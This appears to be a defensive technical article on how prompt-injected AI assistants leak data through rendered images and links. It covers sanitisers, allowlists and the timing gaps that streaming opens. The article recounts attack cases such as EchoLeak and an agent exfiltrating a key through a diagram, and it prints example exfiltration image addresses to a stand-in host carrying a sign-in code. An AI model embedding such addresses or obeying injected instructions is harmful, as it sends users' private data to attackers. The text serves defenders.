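# Output sanitisation and domain allowlists in AI assistants, and the timing gaps that defeat them

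## How an assistant's answer can send data out

An AI assistant passes a person's request to a large language model, which writes a reply one short piece of text at a time, and then displays that reply. Many assistants also read the person's email and files, search the web and operate other services, so the same model processes both private data and text written by strangers. A stranger's text can contain instructions, and if the model follows them, displaying its reply in the browser may send some of the private data to the stranger. Security engineers call this exfiltration, the transfer of private data to someone not entitled to it.

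Output sanitisation and domain allowlists are defences that act after the model has generated text. Sanitisation removes or neutralises the parts of an output that could make a program act. A domain allowlist restricts a page, server or tool to contacting only the listed hosts (named computers on the internet). Websites that display comments from the public have long used both. With assistants, however, a filter can reach the text after the browser has already acted on it, because most assistants show the answer while the model is still writing it.

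### Prompt injection

Prompt injection is text placed in something a model reads so that the model follows it as an instruction. The software developer Simon Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that he named it after SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form ends up running as a database command. Both attacks work because a program mixes trusted and untrusted content. Programmers can reliably prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the data to the database separately, but a language model receives the developer's instructions, the user's question and the web page to be summarised as one sequence of text fragments, with nothing that reliably marks which parts it should follow as instructions.

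An attacker can type an instruction into the assistant, which is a direct injection, or leave it in material that the assistant will later read for someone else, which is an indirect injection. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 105 studies of language models and web security, rates the indirect form as the greater risk in practice because external sources give attackers many more ways to deliver it. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026), a group from the security firm Gray Swan, several AI developers and the US and UK government AI institutes, list emails, documents and code repositories among the places where such instructions can sit. The victim may notice nothing odd, because an email can contain white text on a white background, which a person overlooks but a model reads like any other text.

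Willison distinguishes prompt injection from jailbreaking, in which a user talks a model into breaking its developer's rules. A jailbreak mostly embarrasses the developer, and Willison reports that people who confuse the two often dismiss prompt injection as somebody else's problem. Indirect injection harms the user, who asked for nothing improper.

OWASP, a community group that publishes widely used lists of web security risks, has separate entries for prompt injection and "improper output handling" in its list for language models. Singh and colleagues trace them to different programming weaknesses. Prompt injection comes from how an application assembles the model's input, and improper output handling from how it encodes the model's output before passing it to another program. Fixing one can leave the other open. Sanitisation and allowlists belong to the output side, and must be designed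 on the assumption that an injection has already succeeded.

### From token to request

Suppose a user asks a browser-based assistant to summarise the morning's email. The model writes its reply as tokens, text fragments that are often only a few characters long, so a single web address may take a dozen or more of them. The assistant's server gathers the tokens and sends them to the browser in small chunks, over a connection that stays open until the answer ends. Sending and displaying an answer piece by piece while the model is still writing it is called streaming. Where one chunk ends and the next begins depends on network and server timing, not on the structure of the text, so an address can be split between two chunks.

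A script in the page adds each new chunk to the text already received. At this stage the text is usually Markdown, a notation in which double asterisks around a phrase make it bold, and an exclamation mark followed by square and round brackets makes an image. The script then converts the Markdown to HTML, the language of web pages, though some assistants do the conversion on the server and stream HTML instead. Markdown text can also contain HTML, which some converters leave unchanged. Markup here means Markdown or HTML that a program turns into formatted display, links or images.

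So far the answer is only a string of characters in the browser's memory. When the script puts the HTML into the live document, the page on display, the browser turns it into a tree of objects, one for each paragraph, link and image. It normally starts downloading each image straight away by looking up the host's name, opening a connection and sending a request that contains the rest of the address. In the usual design, nobody has to approve any step between the model producing its tokens and the browser sending that request.

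The converter and the browser both work as they should, so it is hard to point to a broken component in this chain. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026) find the same pattern across a range of attacks on web applications in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*. They argue that the model usually carries the attacker's influence to another component that trusts its output, rather than creating the vulnerability itself. For instance, a malicious script written by a model does harm only once the page displays it as live content. For an image, the trusting component is the page that accepts any address the model supplies.

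### Why an image needs no click

Browsers load images automatically so that readers can see a complete page without approving each one. This means that whoever chooses an image's address can make the reader's browser contact a host of their choosing. The image can be a single transparent pixel, or it can be missing altogether, since the server receives the full address before it can reply that the file does not exist.

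Unlike an image, a link ordinarily sends no request to its destination until somebody clicks it. An attacker limited to links therefore has to write a label that the user will want to follow, perhaps an invitation to sign in again, and the user has a chance to inspect the address first. Few people read a long address to the end, so the click is a weak safeguard, and Willison counts clickable links among the channels that can carry stolen data. Some chat services remove even that safeguard by fetching every linked page to build a preview, which sends the request without a click, much as an image does.

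An image can leak data even when it loads outside the chat window. Willison, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, notes a 2026 flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork. The agent could email its own user without approval, and images in the message could leak data when the user opened it. Anyone assessing an assistant has to find every place where its text is displayed, including emails, exported documents and notifications.

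### A six-digit code in an image address

The domain example.com is one of a few that internet standards reserve for documentation, so it can stand in for an attacker's server without harm to anyone. Suppose that the user's mailbox holds a message with the sign-in code 482913, and that injected text in a second email has led the model to finish its summary with an image. The model composes the image's address and puts the code inside it:

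`https://img.example.com/dot.png?c=482913`

Everything after the question mark is a query string, the part of an address in which web pages commonly pass small values to a server. The browser requests the picture. The receiving server, like most web servers in their ordinary configuration, adds a line to its access log:

`203.0.113.7 - - [07/Oct/2026:09:14:52 +0000] "GET /dot.png?c=482913 HTTP/1.1" 404 153 "https://assistant.example/" "Mozilla/5.0 ..."`

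From left to right, the line contains the network address that sent the request, the time, the request with the code in it, a status of 404 (no such picture), the size of the reply in bytes, the site whose page asked for the image, and a description of the browser. The attacker needs no other software. Encryption does not protect the code, because the attacker's server is the intended endpoint of the encrypted connection. The log line appears within moments of the request, when a short-lived code is probably still valid. The user sees an accurate summary of the morning's email with, at most, a broken-image icon underneath.

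An answer can leak longer secrets the same way. The model can replace spaces and punctuation with the numeric codes that web addresses use for them, and an address can run to thousands of characters, enough for several paragraphs of a private letter. The data can also go in the file name or host name, where a filter that strips only query strings would miss it.

### Three conditions, and the one that defenders cut

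Willison's "lethal trifecta" is the combination, in one assistant, of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. In the example, the mailbox with the code provides the first, the stranger's email the second, and the image the third. Removing any one of them would prevent this theft.

Removing private data defeats the purpose of most assistants, since people connect their mail and files to ask about them. Removing untrusted content limits them nearly as much, because inboxes and the web consist largely of text written by other people. The makers of Cursor, a programming tool, responded to one report of this kind by advising users to connect only sources with trusted content. Willison thought this advice was hard to follow because attackers have so many ways to get text in front of a model.

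Willison judges the outbound channel to be generally the easiest of the three conditions to remove. An email summary loses little if it cannot display images from arbitrary servers, and the rule that blocks them is ordinary code that gives the same result every time. His list of affected products starts with ChatGPT in April 2023 and includes assistants from Google, Microsoft, Slack, Anthropic and others. He reports that the vendors fixed almost all of these flaws promptly, usually by closing the channel.

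Images are only one way to send data out. Any tool that can make a web request can do the same, and Willison calls the possible routes almost limitless. He worries particularly about users who connect tools of their own choosing through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for linking assistants to outside services, because no vendor has examined the resulting combination. Output defences protect confidentiality, but they leave the injection in place. A model acting on a stranger's instructions can still falsify a summary or, if it has the tools, delete messages.

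### Why the model's own resistance is not enough

Developers also train models to ignore injected instructions, and the results have improved. Anthropic included prompt injection in its safety evaluations of Claude Opus 5, its July 2026 model. On an indirect-injection benchmark, attackers succeeded 0.2% of the time with one attempt and 2.0% of the time within 15 attempts (figures reproduced in Schneier, 2026, *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*). No attack worked in the 129 browser scenarios that Anthropic tested, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*.

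Those are low rates for a fixed test, but a real attacker chooses how often to try. If 0.2% held outside the benchmark, one hostile message to each of 10,000 mailboxes would succeed about 20 times. Other models do far worse. iAfrica's *New Independent Tracker Finds Wide Safety Gaps Between AI Models* reports that, in Gray Swan's public tracker, 15 attacks compromised the best model 2.3% of the time and the worst, an open model that anyone can host, 94.3% of the time. Willison argues that 99% is a failing grade in application security because an adversary will search for the remaining 1%. By contrast, a rule about which hosts a browser may contact applies in the same way however persuasive the injected text is.

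### What each output defence acts on

Sanitisation acts on the text of the model's reply. In the example, a filter would delete the image markup or show the address as plain text, so the browser would have nothing to fetch. The filter can also remove or rewrite links. Sanitisation relies on the filter recognising every form of markup that can cause a request and finishing before the text reaches the live document. The timing gap is the interval between when markup can cause a request and when the filter neutralises it.

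An allowlist acts on the request. For a web page the usual instrument is a content security policy (CSP), a rule set sent with the page that tells the browser which hosts each kind of resource may come from. An assistant's page might arrive with this one:

`Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' https://static.assistant.example`

The line permits images from the page's own site and from one named host. When the image from img.example.com enters the document, the browser compares its host with the list, finds no match and sends nothing. Because this check happens at the moment of the request, a CSP still holds when a sanitiser runs late or misses an unusual piece of markup. However, if a permitted host stores whatever visitors send to it, an attacker can collect data there as easily as on a private server. Browsers also have no generally supported CSP rule for where an ordinary link may lead,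 so the sanitiser has to handle links.

Neither a sanitiser in the page nor a CSP can block a server-side fetch, which is a request made by a service's own computers. When an assistant opens a web page with a browsing tool, the request typically starts in the provider's data centre, so the log line in the example would show the provider's network address instead of the user's. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built a test application called TicketOracle to study such requests and tried five attack scenarios on seven models. The models differed widely in how easily an attacker could steer them into making the request, but the vulnerability came from the design of the application around them. These requests need their own allowlist, which the developer has to enforce in the tool or on the provider's network.

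## Choosing what the answer may contain: plain text, limited Markdown or cleaned HTML

The more formatting a page displays, the more its sanitiser has to filter. Plain text needs almost no filtering, while HTML needs a filter that covers every feature able to start a request. Developers usually choose how much formatting to allow when they pick a rendering library, often by accepting its defaults. From strictest to loosest, they can escape everything, put the answer in a code block, allow Markdown without images or raw HTML, or allow sanitised HTML. Each option protects the user only if it takes effect before the text reaches the live document.

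### Escaping everything

Escaping replaces characters with special meaning in HTML with codes that the browser displays as ordinary characters. The less-than sign becomes `&lt;`, for instance, so an image tag in the reply appears as text rather than as an image. A script can get the same result by assigning the reply to an element's `textContent` property, which bypasses the HTML parser. Neither method has to recognise dangerous tags, so both still work when browsers add new ones.

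If answers are shown as plain text, users lose all formatting. Headings appear with their hash signs, tables turn into rows of vertical bars, and users can't click links. That hardly matters for a one-line answer, but it makes a long comparison tiresome to read.

Escaping usually goes wrong because another program processes the text afterwards. HTML escaping leaves Markdown's image notation intact, so if a page escapes the reply and then passes it to a Markdown converter, the converter still produces an image. The *Security* guide for Streamdown, a Markdown renderer designed for AI output, explains how to show HTML tags as text, but that setting alone does not stop Markdown images. Chat services that build link previews from bare addresses cause a similar problem when an assistant posts its escaped reply to them. A developer therefore has to escape for the last program that will interpret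 the text.

### Wrapping the answer in a code block

A Markdown code block displays the text between two fences, usually lines of three backticks, exactly as written. Wrapping a whole reply in one is an easy way to switch off Markdown in a channel the developer does not control, such as a chat service that always renders it. Users lose as much formatting as with escaping, and long lines may run off the side of the screen. Program code is normally displayed in a code block anyway.

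If a program puts the reply in a code block fenced with three backticks, a line of three backticks in the reply closes the block, and the converter formats the rest as Markdown. An attacker can get the model to write that line. Under CommonMark, a widely used specification of Markdown, a closing fence must be at least as long as the opening one, so the program can find the longest run of backticks in the reply and open the block with a longer fence. Where the developer controls the page, it is simpler to create a code element and assign the reply to it as text, because there is no fence to close.

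Rendering a code block can also produce more than plain text. Many renderers run a program, such as a highlighter that colours the code, when the opening fence carries a particular language label. TanStack, which publishes open-source web libraries, advises developers to audit or sanitise the highlighter's output.

Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025), in *Takedown*, found a leak in a diagram tool of this sort. The KAIST group examined eight coding agents, assistants that read and edit a programmer's files and run commands, by intercepting their traffic and reverse-engineering some of the programs. They withheld the products' names because the vendors were still handling the reports. One agent, which they call A2, drew diagrams with Mermaid, which turns short text descriptions into charts. Mermaid can display an image from a web address inside a shape, and A2 fetched that image without asking the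 user.

To test the whole chain, the researchers hid instructions in an issue (a bug report) in their own code repository and had A2 retrieve the issue. A2 read a settings file outside the project without approval, put the file's access key into the address of an image in a diagram, and sent the key out when it drew the diagram. The vendor already knew of the flaw and has patched it.

A filter that follows Markdown's rules would have let the diagram through, because it counted as a block of code. If an extension replaces part of the answer with its own output, that output needs the same restrictions on images and links as the rest of the answer. A diagram tool should run with external images turned off.

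### Markdown without images or raw HTML

With limited Markdown, the converter keeps headings, emphasis, lists, tables and code, discards images, and either drops HTML tags or shows them as text. Discarding images removes the request that the browser would otherwise send without a click. Users lose pictures and any layout that Markdown cannot express, but this is a small loss in most chat answers. The package *harden-react-markdown*, a wrapper for a popular converter, shows "Image blocked" and the picture's description in place of each blocked image. By default it also blocks every external link until the developer lists the permitted ones.

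GitHub chose a looser version for its coding assistant, stopping a leak by disabling Markdown images that point to untrusted domains (Willison, 2024, *GitHub Copilot Chat*). Google responded differently when a researcher reported in late 2025 that hidden instructions could leak data through Markdown images from Antigravity, its own coding tool. Willison quotes the researcher as saying that Google flagged the report as intended behaviour.

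A renderer's default settings may be much looser than its documentation first suggests. Streamdown's documentation describes security as a top priority, yet the defaults allow images and links from any address, and the same documentation recommends tighter settings for untrusted text. Its rehype-sanitize plugin strips dangerous tags, and its rehype-harden plugin checks where links and images point. A developer who supplies a custom plugin list to tighten the address rules replaces both default plugins, and so loses the tag stripping unless the new list includes rehype-sanitize.

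Helicone, a service that records applications' exchanges with language models, had the kind of flaw that such an omission would cause. According to *security* (ink-the-squid, 2026), a code change that Helicone accepted on 19 February 2026, Helicone's page let raw HTML through and rehype-harden cleaned only link and image tags. A model's reply could therefore include an inline frame (a page within the page) whose script stole the reader's sign-in cookie. The account of the plugin agrees with the *rehype-harden* documentation, which gives its purpose as keeping unexpected images and links out of untrusted Markdown, so it cannot be relied on to remove frames or forms. The code change does not mention rehype-sanitize, the plugin meant to remove them.

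The Helicone contributor fixed the flaw by using pattern matching to delete dangerous tags from the Markdown text before the renderer received it. The usual HTML sanitiser would have treated the Markdown as HTML and garbled the backticks and asterisks. But pattern matching relies on a guess about how the converter and the browser will later read the text. The documentation of *markdown sanitizers* recommends cleaning the final HTML wherever the developer controls the rendering, and cleaning the Markdown text only when a third party such as GitHub renders it. The Helicone change also addresses script theft. The contributor lists frames, forms and scripts among the tags to remove, but not images, so image leaks still depend on how Helicone configures rehype-harden.

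Links remain a problem with this choice even when everything works as intended. A page that doesn't need clickable links can show addresses as plain text, and a page that cites sources can restrict links to sites on an allowlist.

### HTML passed through a sanitiser

An HTML sanitiser parses the text into a tree of elements and removes any element or attribute that its lists do not permit. Users keep nearly all the formatting. But developers built the common sanitisers to stop cross-site scripting, an attack in which a stranger's script runs inside a page with the reader's permissions. An ordinary image tag runs no script, so a sanitiser built for that purpose does not need to remove it.

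*DOMPurify*, a widely used sanitiser from the German security firm Cure53, permits HTML, SVG (a format for drawings) and MathML (a notation for formulas) by default. Its default tag list includes images, video, forms, hyperlinks and style rules. Cure53's *pentest report dompurify*, an old security review about a different flaw, includes a demonstration that depends on the library letting an image tag through when no custom tag list is set.

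Suppose the assistant's page runs DOMPurify with its default settings on the morning summary from the earlier example. The library accepts the image whose address ends in 482913, and the browser requests it. If the tag also carried an `onerror` attribute, which runs a script when an image fails to load, DOMPurify would delete the attribute but keep the image, so the attacker would still get the code. An attacker could also use a form that imitates a sign-in box and sends whatever the user types to an outside server.

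Forbidding the image tag alone is not enough. Video posters, image buttons, style rules with a background picture and SVG's own image element can all make the browser fetch something. A short list of permitted tags is safer than a long list of banned ones, and DOMPurify's own demonstrations include one that permits little more than paragraphs and text. For a chat answer without links, a setting like this would do:

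```
DOMPurify.sanitize(html, {
  ALLOWED_TAGS: ['p', 'strong', 'em', 'ul', 'ol', 'li', 'pre', 'code'],
  ALLOWED_ATTR: [],
  ALLOW_DATA_ATTR: false
});
```

Without the last line, DOMPurify keeps custom attributes whose names begin with `data-`, and some pages run scripts that load pictures from addresses in those attributes. Writing the lists out in every call also protects against a flaw that GitLab describes in its advisory database. Developers can attach a function, called a hook, that adjusts DOMPurify's decisions. In the affected versions, if a hook permitted an extra tag for one answer, DOMPurify permanently added that tag to its default list and permitted it in every later call that didn't supply its own list.

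Browser makers are adding a sanitiser to the browser. The Web Platform Incubator Community Group's *HTML Sanitizer API*, a draft specification, defines the lists it filters by, and WHATWG's *Dynamic markup insertion*, a chapter of the HTML Standard, now has a companion section on HTML sanitisation. The draft's default list is much stricter than DOMPurify's. It allows text formatting, tables, formulas, simple drawings and hyperlinks, but not image, video, form or style elements.

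Developers can easily lose that protection by supplying their own settings, even an empty settings object. The browser then drops the default list and guarantees only the removal of items that can run scripts. MDN's *Default sanitizer configuration*, part of a standard reference for web developers, also warns that custom settings do not include the default's extra removals. The table compares the three cases.

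| Markup in the answer | DOMPurify, default settings | Browser sanitiser, default settings | Browser sanitiser, custom settings that do not mention the item |
|---|---|---|---|
| Image | Kept | Removed | Kept if the settings ban listed tags, removed if they permit only listed tags |
| Video or audio | Kept | Removed | As for images |
| Form | Kept | Removed | As for images |
| Style element | Kept | Removed | As for images |
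| Hyperlink | Kept | Kept | As for images |
| Script, inline frame | Removed | Removed | Removed |

Alfy's (2026) tutorial on the browser sanitiser shows an image surviving the default settings with only its `onerror` attribute removed. Under the specification, the browser removes the whole image, because images are not on the default list of allowed elements. The tutorial's result is correct only for custom settings that allow images. A developer who trusted the example could loosen the settings without noticing any difference.

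The specification's guarantee is limited because it uses "unsafe" only for content that will execute JavaScript. It blocks links that run scripts but allows others, since following a link is not in itself a scripting threat. Frederik Braun, one of the specification's editors, says the default list goes further, to guard against spoofing and phishing (*Composing Sanitizer configurations*). However, the default keeps a few SVG attributes, such as `fill` and `cursor`, whose values can contain a web address. Anyone relying on it against exfiltration should test whether the browsers they support fetch those addresses.

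### HTML parsed twice

A sanitiser with the right list can still fail if the browser parses the cleaned text differently. As Braun explains in *Why the Sanitizer API is just setHTML()*, the sanitiser usually parses the text into a tree, removes disallowed content, and turns the tree back into a string. The page then inserts that string, so the browser parses it again, this time inside a particular element of the page. HTML's parsing rules depend on the surrounding element, so the same characters can produce a different tree. Security researchers call attacks that exploit this difference mutated cross-site scripting.

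Fluid Attacks' *DOMPurify mXSS via Re-Contextualization* describes an example in which an application cleaned some HTML and then placed the result inside a wrapper such as `xmp`, an obsolete element whose contents the browser treats as plain text until it reaches the closing tag. An attacker had put a closing tag and an image tag inside the value of an attribute. DOMPurify correctly left them alone because, in the first parse, they were only characters in that value. When the browser parsed the wrapped result, the closing tag ended the wrapper and the image tag became an actual image element. A list that banned images would not have helped, because DOMPurify never encountered an image element.

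The danger increases with every program that processes the text after it is cleaned. After cleaning the answer, an assistant's page might run a highlighter, a tool that turns bare addresses into links, and another that inserts icons. Cure53 warns that changing the HTML after sanitisation can undo its effect. The sanitiser should therefore run last and return a DOM tree that the page inserts directly. DOMPurify can return a tree instead of a string, and the browser's new `setHTML` method parses the text once, in the element that will display it.

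### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers questions from an employee's email and files. Microsoft protected it with a classifier to detect injected instructions in what Copilot read, a filter to remove external links from its answers, and a CSP. In January 2025, researchers at the security company Aim Security found a way past all three, which they named EchoLeak. The flaw is listed as CVE-2025-32711. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reconstructs the attack from published accounts.

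The attacker needed only to send the employee an email. It phrased the instructions as a business request to the human recipient, and the classifier let them through. It also asked that the answer not mention the email, so the employee wouldn't see where the answer had gone wrong. Nothing happened when the email arrived. When the employee later asked Copilot about their work, Copilot's search could retrieve the email along with internal documents, and the model would follow the email's instructions and write confidential details into a web address.

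At that point the link filter should have removed the address. In Markdown's more common notation, a link's address stands in round brackets directly after its label, and the filter looked for that pattern. Markdown also has a reference style, which puts the address elsewhere in the text:

```
Read the [annual report][1] first.

[1]: https://www.example.com/report
```

The converter handled both notations, but the filter recognised only the first, so a reference-style link reached the employee intact. Images can be written in reference style too, and using one instead of a link removed the need for a click.

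The CSP still blocked the attacker's own server, so the researchers looked for a permitted host that would pass the request on. After examining SharePoint, Microsoft's file-sharing service, they chose a preview service in Teams, its chat program, which fetched any address passed to it as a parameter. The image's address pointed to Teams and contained the attacker's address, with the stolen details inside it. The browser's policy allowed the image because it came from a Microsoft host, and Teams then contacted the attacker's server through a server-side fetch.

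Aim Security reported the EchoLeak chain privately, and Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May 2025, so customers didn't have to do anything. Both companies disclosed it on 11 June, and Microsoft said it had no evidence of real attacks. The chain is unusual in passing so many separate defences, but Reddy and Gujral overstate its novelty when they call it the first known case of prompt injection causing data theft in a production system, since Willison's list of affected products starts in 2023.

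### What would have stopped EchoLeak

Reddy and Gujral propose eight mitigations and judge each against the stages of the attack. In the table, "mixing" means Copilot combined a stranger's email with internal documents.

| Mitigation | Would stop | Would fail against |
|---|---|---|
| Tagging outside text in the model's input as data | Mixing, getting past the classifier | The final leak without a click |
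| Answering from internal sources unless the user asks for others | Mixing, getting past the link filter | The final leak |
| Restricting answers to permitted Markdown or a fixed data format | Mixing, getting past the classifier and link filter | The automatic image request, the final leak |
| Allowing or blocking listed addresses | Getting past the link filter, the Teams proxy, the final leak | The automatic image request |
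| A strict CSP | The automatic image request, the Teams proxy, the final leak | None |
| An image proxy that accepts only signed, expiring addresses | The automatic image request, the Teams proxy, the final leak | None |
| Human approval for outside content | Everything except the Teams proxy, which they do not assess | None |
| Monitoring outgoing text for personal data and addresses | None | The final leak |

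These marks are judgements. Reddy and Gujral refer to "our tests" when explaining them, but state in their limitations section that they ran no experiments and did not reproduce the attack. Some marks are also hard to reconcile with the text. They write that EchoLeak "fails by design" if Copilot never uses strangers' email to answer questions about internal projects, yet they mark that rule as failing to prevent the leak.

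The paper's verdict on restricted Markdown depends on whether the restriction allows images. Elsewhere, the paper describes a safe subset of Markdown that includes plain images, which could have carried the data. If Copilot's converter had been unable to produce images, the Teams proxy would have had nothing to fetch, even though the injection had succeeded and the proxy was on the allowlist. Checking links after conversion would also have closed the gap between the two link notations, because the converter turns both into the same kind of link. A strict CSP would have worked only if it had excluded the Teams host or its preview service, since Copilot's existing policy already blocked unknown servers.

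Developers can recreate the Teams weakness by accident. Streamdown's example of rewriting addresses sends every image through the site's own proxy with the original address attached. Unless the proxy checks that address against its own allowlist, it will send any stolen data the address contains to the attacker.

### Matching the choice to the display

Few products need the most permissive format everywhere. An assistant might show notifications as plain text and chat answers as Markdown, and allow HTML only in its report editor. For each need, the table gives the strictest format that meets it and the precaution developers most easily overlook.

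| What users need to see | Strictest workable choice | Precaution |
|---|---|---|
| Short answers, notifications, log entries | Escape everything | Turn off automatic links and previews wherever the text ends up |
| Program code | A code element filled as text | Sanitise the highlighter's output |
| Headings, lists and tables | Markdown without images, raw HTML or clickable links | Check what each extension adds to the page |
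| Citations | The same Markdown, with links to listed sites | Apply the list after conversion, so that it covers every link notation |
| Diagrams | The same Markdown, with a diagram tool that cannot load outside resources | Test image shapes and labels inside diagrams |
| Pictures from the product's own library | The same Markdown, with the model naming a picture and the application supplying its address | Do not accept an address that the model has written |
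| Documents with their own layout | HTML through a sanitiser with a short list of permitted tags and attributes | Sanitise last, and add a CSP for whatever the list misses |

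## Why a filter that runs late protects nothing

When a page waits for the complete reply, a script can easily filter the text and then display it. With streaming, the reply arrives in chunks, and the developer has to decide when the filter runs. If it runs after the markup has entered the page, even a perfect list of permitted tags cannot stop the browser's automatic requests.

### Entry, request and filter

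Whether an image leaks data depends on the order of three events: the markup enters the live document, the browser sends the image's address over the network, and the filter removes or neutralises the markup. The timing gap is the time between the markup entering the document and the filter acting on it. If the filter acts before the markup enters, there is no gap.

A filter must finish before the page's script inserts the text, and it must have examined exactly the text that is inserted. Developers control when that insertion happens. In principle, a filter that acts later can still keep the data private if it acts before the request leaves. Developers cannot rely on this, because the browser controls when to send the request, and the delay varies with the browser and the state of the connection. Data can also escape before the image request. If the attacker has had the data placed in the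 host name, the browser's lookup of that name can deliver it to a name server that the attacker runs.

### An image at token 120

Suppose the model writes the morning email summary at 50 tokens a second. The injected text has told it to put the image near the top, and the closing bracket of the image tag arrives with token 120, which is 120 / 50 = 2.4 seconds into the answer. Until then the browser has only part of a tag and creates no image. The answer ends at token 600, after 12 seconds. Assume too that the page inserts each token as it arrives, and that the browser sends the image request 20 milliseconds (ms) after the image enters the page. These figures are illustrative, not measurements.

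| Where the filter runs | Image enters | Request leaves | Filter acts | Timing gap |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Once, at the end of the answer | 2.40 s | 2.42 s | 12.00 s | 9.6 s |
| 100 ms after each insertion | 2.40 s | 2.42 s | 2.50 s | 0.1 s |
| Before each insertion, taking 400 ms | Never | Never | 2.80 s | None |

An attacker can widen the 9.6-second gap by asking for the image first and a long summary after it. If the user closes the tab after 8 seconds, a filter that waits for the end of the response never runs.

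Cleaning up 100 ms after each insertion makes the gap about a hundred times shorter, but the request still leaves 80 ms before the clean-up. With these numbers, a clean-up after 10 ms would stop the request, but it would be too late on a connection where the request leaves in 5 ms.

The filter that runs before insertion can be slow, because no image exists while it works. The user reads each piece of the answer 0.4 seconds later. OpenAI chose this kind of check for ChatGPT. As Willison (2023) reports in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, the page calls an OpenAI service to check whether an image is safe before displaying it. The network round trip takes far longer than a filter in the page. The delay itself exposes nothing, but the check can still fail if the service approves the wrong address.

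A late filter gives some protection against links, because a link leaks data only if the user clicks it before the filter runs. It also cleans the version of the answer that the user copies or exports. But it removes the visible trace of an image that has already leaked data, so anyone who inspects only the finished answer will think the filter worked.

### Check-then-use errors

Programmers have long known a related mistake, in which a program checks a resource and then uses it, although the resource can change in between. *CWE-367*, an entry in the catalogue of software weaknesses maintained by the US non-profit MITRE, includes the example of a program that checks that the user may write to a file and then opens the file by name. If an attacker replaces the file with a link to a different one between those two steps, the program writes to a file that the user has no permission to change.

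A late filter checks the output after the browser has already used it. In the file example, the attacker has to make the swap within a short window and may need many attempts. An attacker who relies on an unfiltered image doesn't have to time anything, because the browser automatically sends the request every time the page inserts the image.

This difference weakens one of the usual remedies. Where a program cannot combine the check and the use, MITRE suggests shortening the time between them, with the caveat that this "will not fix the problem" and only makes an attack harder. In the worked example, shortening the gap from 9.6 seconds to 100 ms does not even make the attack harder, since the request leaves in both cases. MITRE also suggests checking again after the use. A program that has written to the wrong file may be able to restore it, but a page cannot take back an address that has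 reached a stranger's server.

The practice of locking a resource before checking it carries over much better. An assistant can do this by keeping text out of the live document until the filter has finished checking it.

### When the browser requests an image

The worked example assumed a delay of 20 ms between entry and request. The HTML Standard, which WHATWG maintains, does not fix that delay, but it does specify what starts the request. Under its rules, browsers fetch images immediately by default, starting the image-loading procedure whenever a parser or script creates an image element and again whenever a script changes the image's address.

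The procedure waits for the running script to finish before it fetches the image, so a script that sets several attributes in a row triggers only one request, for the last version. It does this by queuing a microtask, a small job that the browser runs as soon as the current script finishes and before any timers or mouse clicks. A clean-up on a timer, even with a delay of zero, therefore runs after the fetch has begun.

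An image does not have to be attached to the page for this to happen. The standard requires only that the element belong to a "fully active" document, which in practice means the page open in the tab. An element that the page's script creates belongs to that document from the start. This catches out developers who clean a reply in a scratch element before displaying it:

```
const scratch = document.createElement('div');
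scratch.innerHTML = reply;      // the browser creates the image here
scratch.querySelectorAll('img').forEach(img => img.remove());
answer.append(scratch);         // no image in the page, but the request is on its way
```

The browser queued the fetch when the second line created the element, so the filter ran too late, even though the code appears to filter before insertion and the user never sees an image. For an image, then, entry happens when the element is created in the live document, whether or not it is visible. If the script instead uses the browser's `DOMParser` to parse the reply into a separate, inactive document, the image doesn't load unless the script later moves it into the live page.

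Removing the element immediately does not help, as the example shows. The standard has no step that cancels the fetch when an ordinary image leaves the page, and it requires the browser to keep the element in memory while the procedure runs. Emptying the image's address works if the script does it before the microtask runs. The script must also empty `srcset`, which lists alternative versions of the image, and deal with any `picture` element around the image, because the browser can take an address from either. If the script empties the address after the fetch has started, the browser abandons the download, but the server may already have the request.

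Even emptying the address within the same script may not work in every browser. In a 2021 bug report, *img current request should be updated off a microtask*, McCormack wrote that WebKit, the engine behind Safari, updated an image's current request immediately instead of waiting for a microtask. He was certain only that scripts could read the new address straight away, and WebKit may have changed since. A defence that depends on emptying the address before the microtask runs needs testing in each browser and after each update.

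Lazy loading, which delays an image's request until the image is near the visible part of the page, offers little protection because the newest lines of a chat answer are normally in view.

When an assistant streams HTML from the server as part of the page itself, a filter has even less time to act. WHATWG notes that some browsers speed up page loading by downloading images named in the HTML before scripts can run. A filter written as a script in that page can therefore start after the browser has requested the image.

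Browser makers are unlikely to fix the problem by delaying image loading. The standard acknowledges that automatic image loading lets a page probe the user's local network. It allows browsers to impose stricter rules, but notes that such rules are typically incompatible with existing websites.

### Filtering at the end, sometimes by default

A team may write its filter for complete replies and later turn on streaming without moving the filter. The page then displays unfiltered text until the reply is complete. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes this gap in Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise Search, which displayed raw HTML during streaming and wrapped it in a code block only afterwards. Wrapping the HTML before display would have neutralised it.

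Developers can also create the gap by changing a setting. Amazon Bedrock, a service for running language models, offers guardrails that screen a model's output for unwanted content. According to AWS's *Configure streaming response behavior to filter content*, the default mode holds each piece of the answer until the scan finishes. The asynchronous mode sends each piece immediately, scans in the background, and blocks only what comes after the first bad piece. AWS does not offer masking of sensitive information in asynchronous mode, presumably because it cannot mask text that the user has already received.

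OpenAI's *Streaming vs Blocking*, the documentation for a similar product, describes the same trade-off. By default, the program completes every check before it shows any output. With streaming on, it shows output while the output checks are still running, and the documentation warns that content that breaks the rules may appear briefly.

By default, another guardrails toolkit streams output before checking it, according to a copy of its documentation hosted by Mintlify. It checks output in chunks of 200 tokens. At 50 tokens a second, a chunk takes 4 seconds to complete, so the check could not start until 1.6 seconds after the image in the worked example had entered the page.

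These products mainly screen for content such as insults or personal details. A second's exposure may be acceptable when the harm comes from somebody reading the text, but loading an image sends its data before anyone has read the sentence around it. A developer who adds an image filter to one of these products should check which mode the product runs in, because the filter will run as late as the other checks.

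### Filtering each chunk alone

A filter can run before insertion and still miss the image if it examines each chunk separately. The network might deliver the example tag in two parts:

```
<img src="https://img.exam
ple.com/dot.png?c=482913">
```

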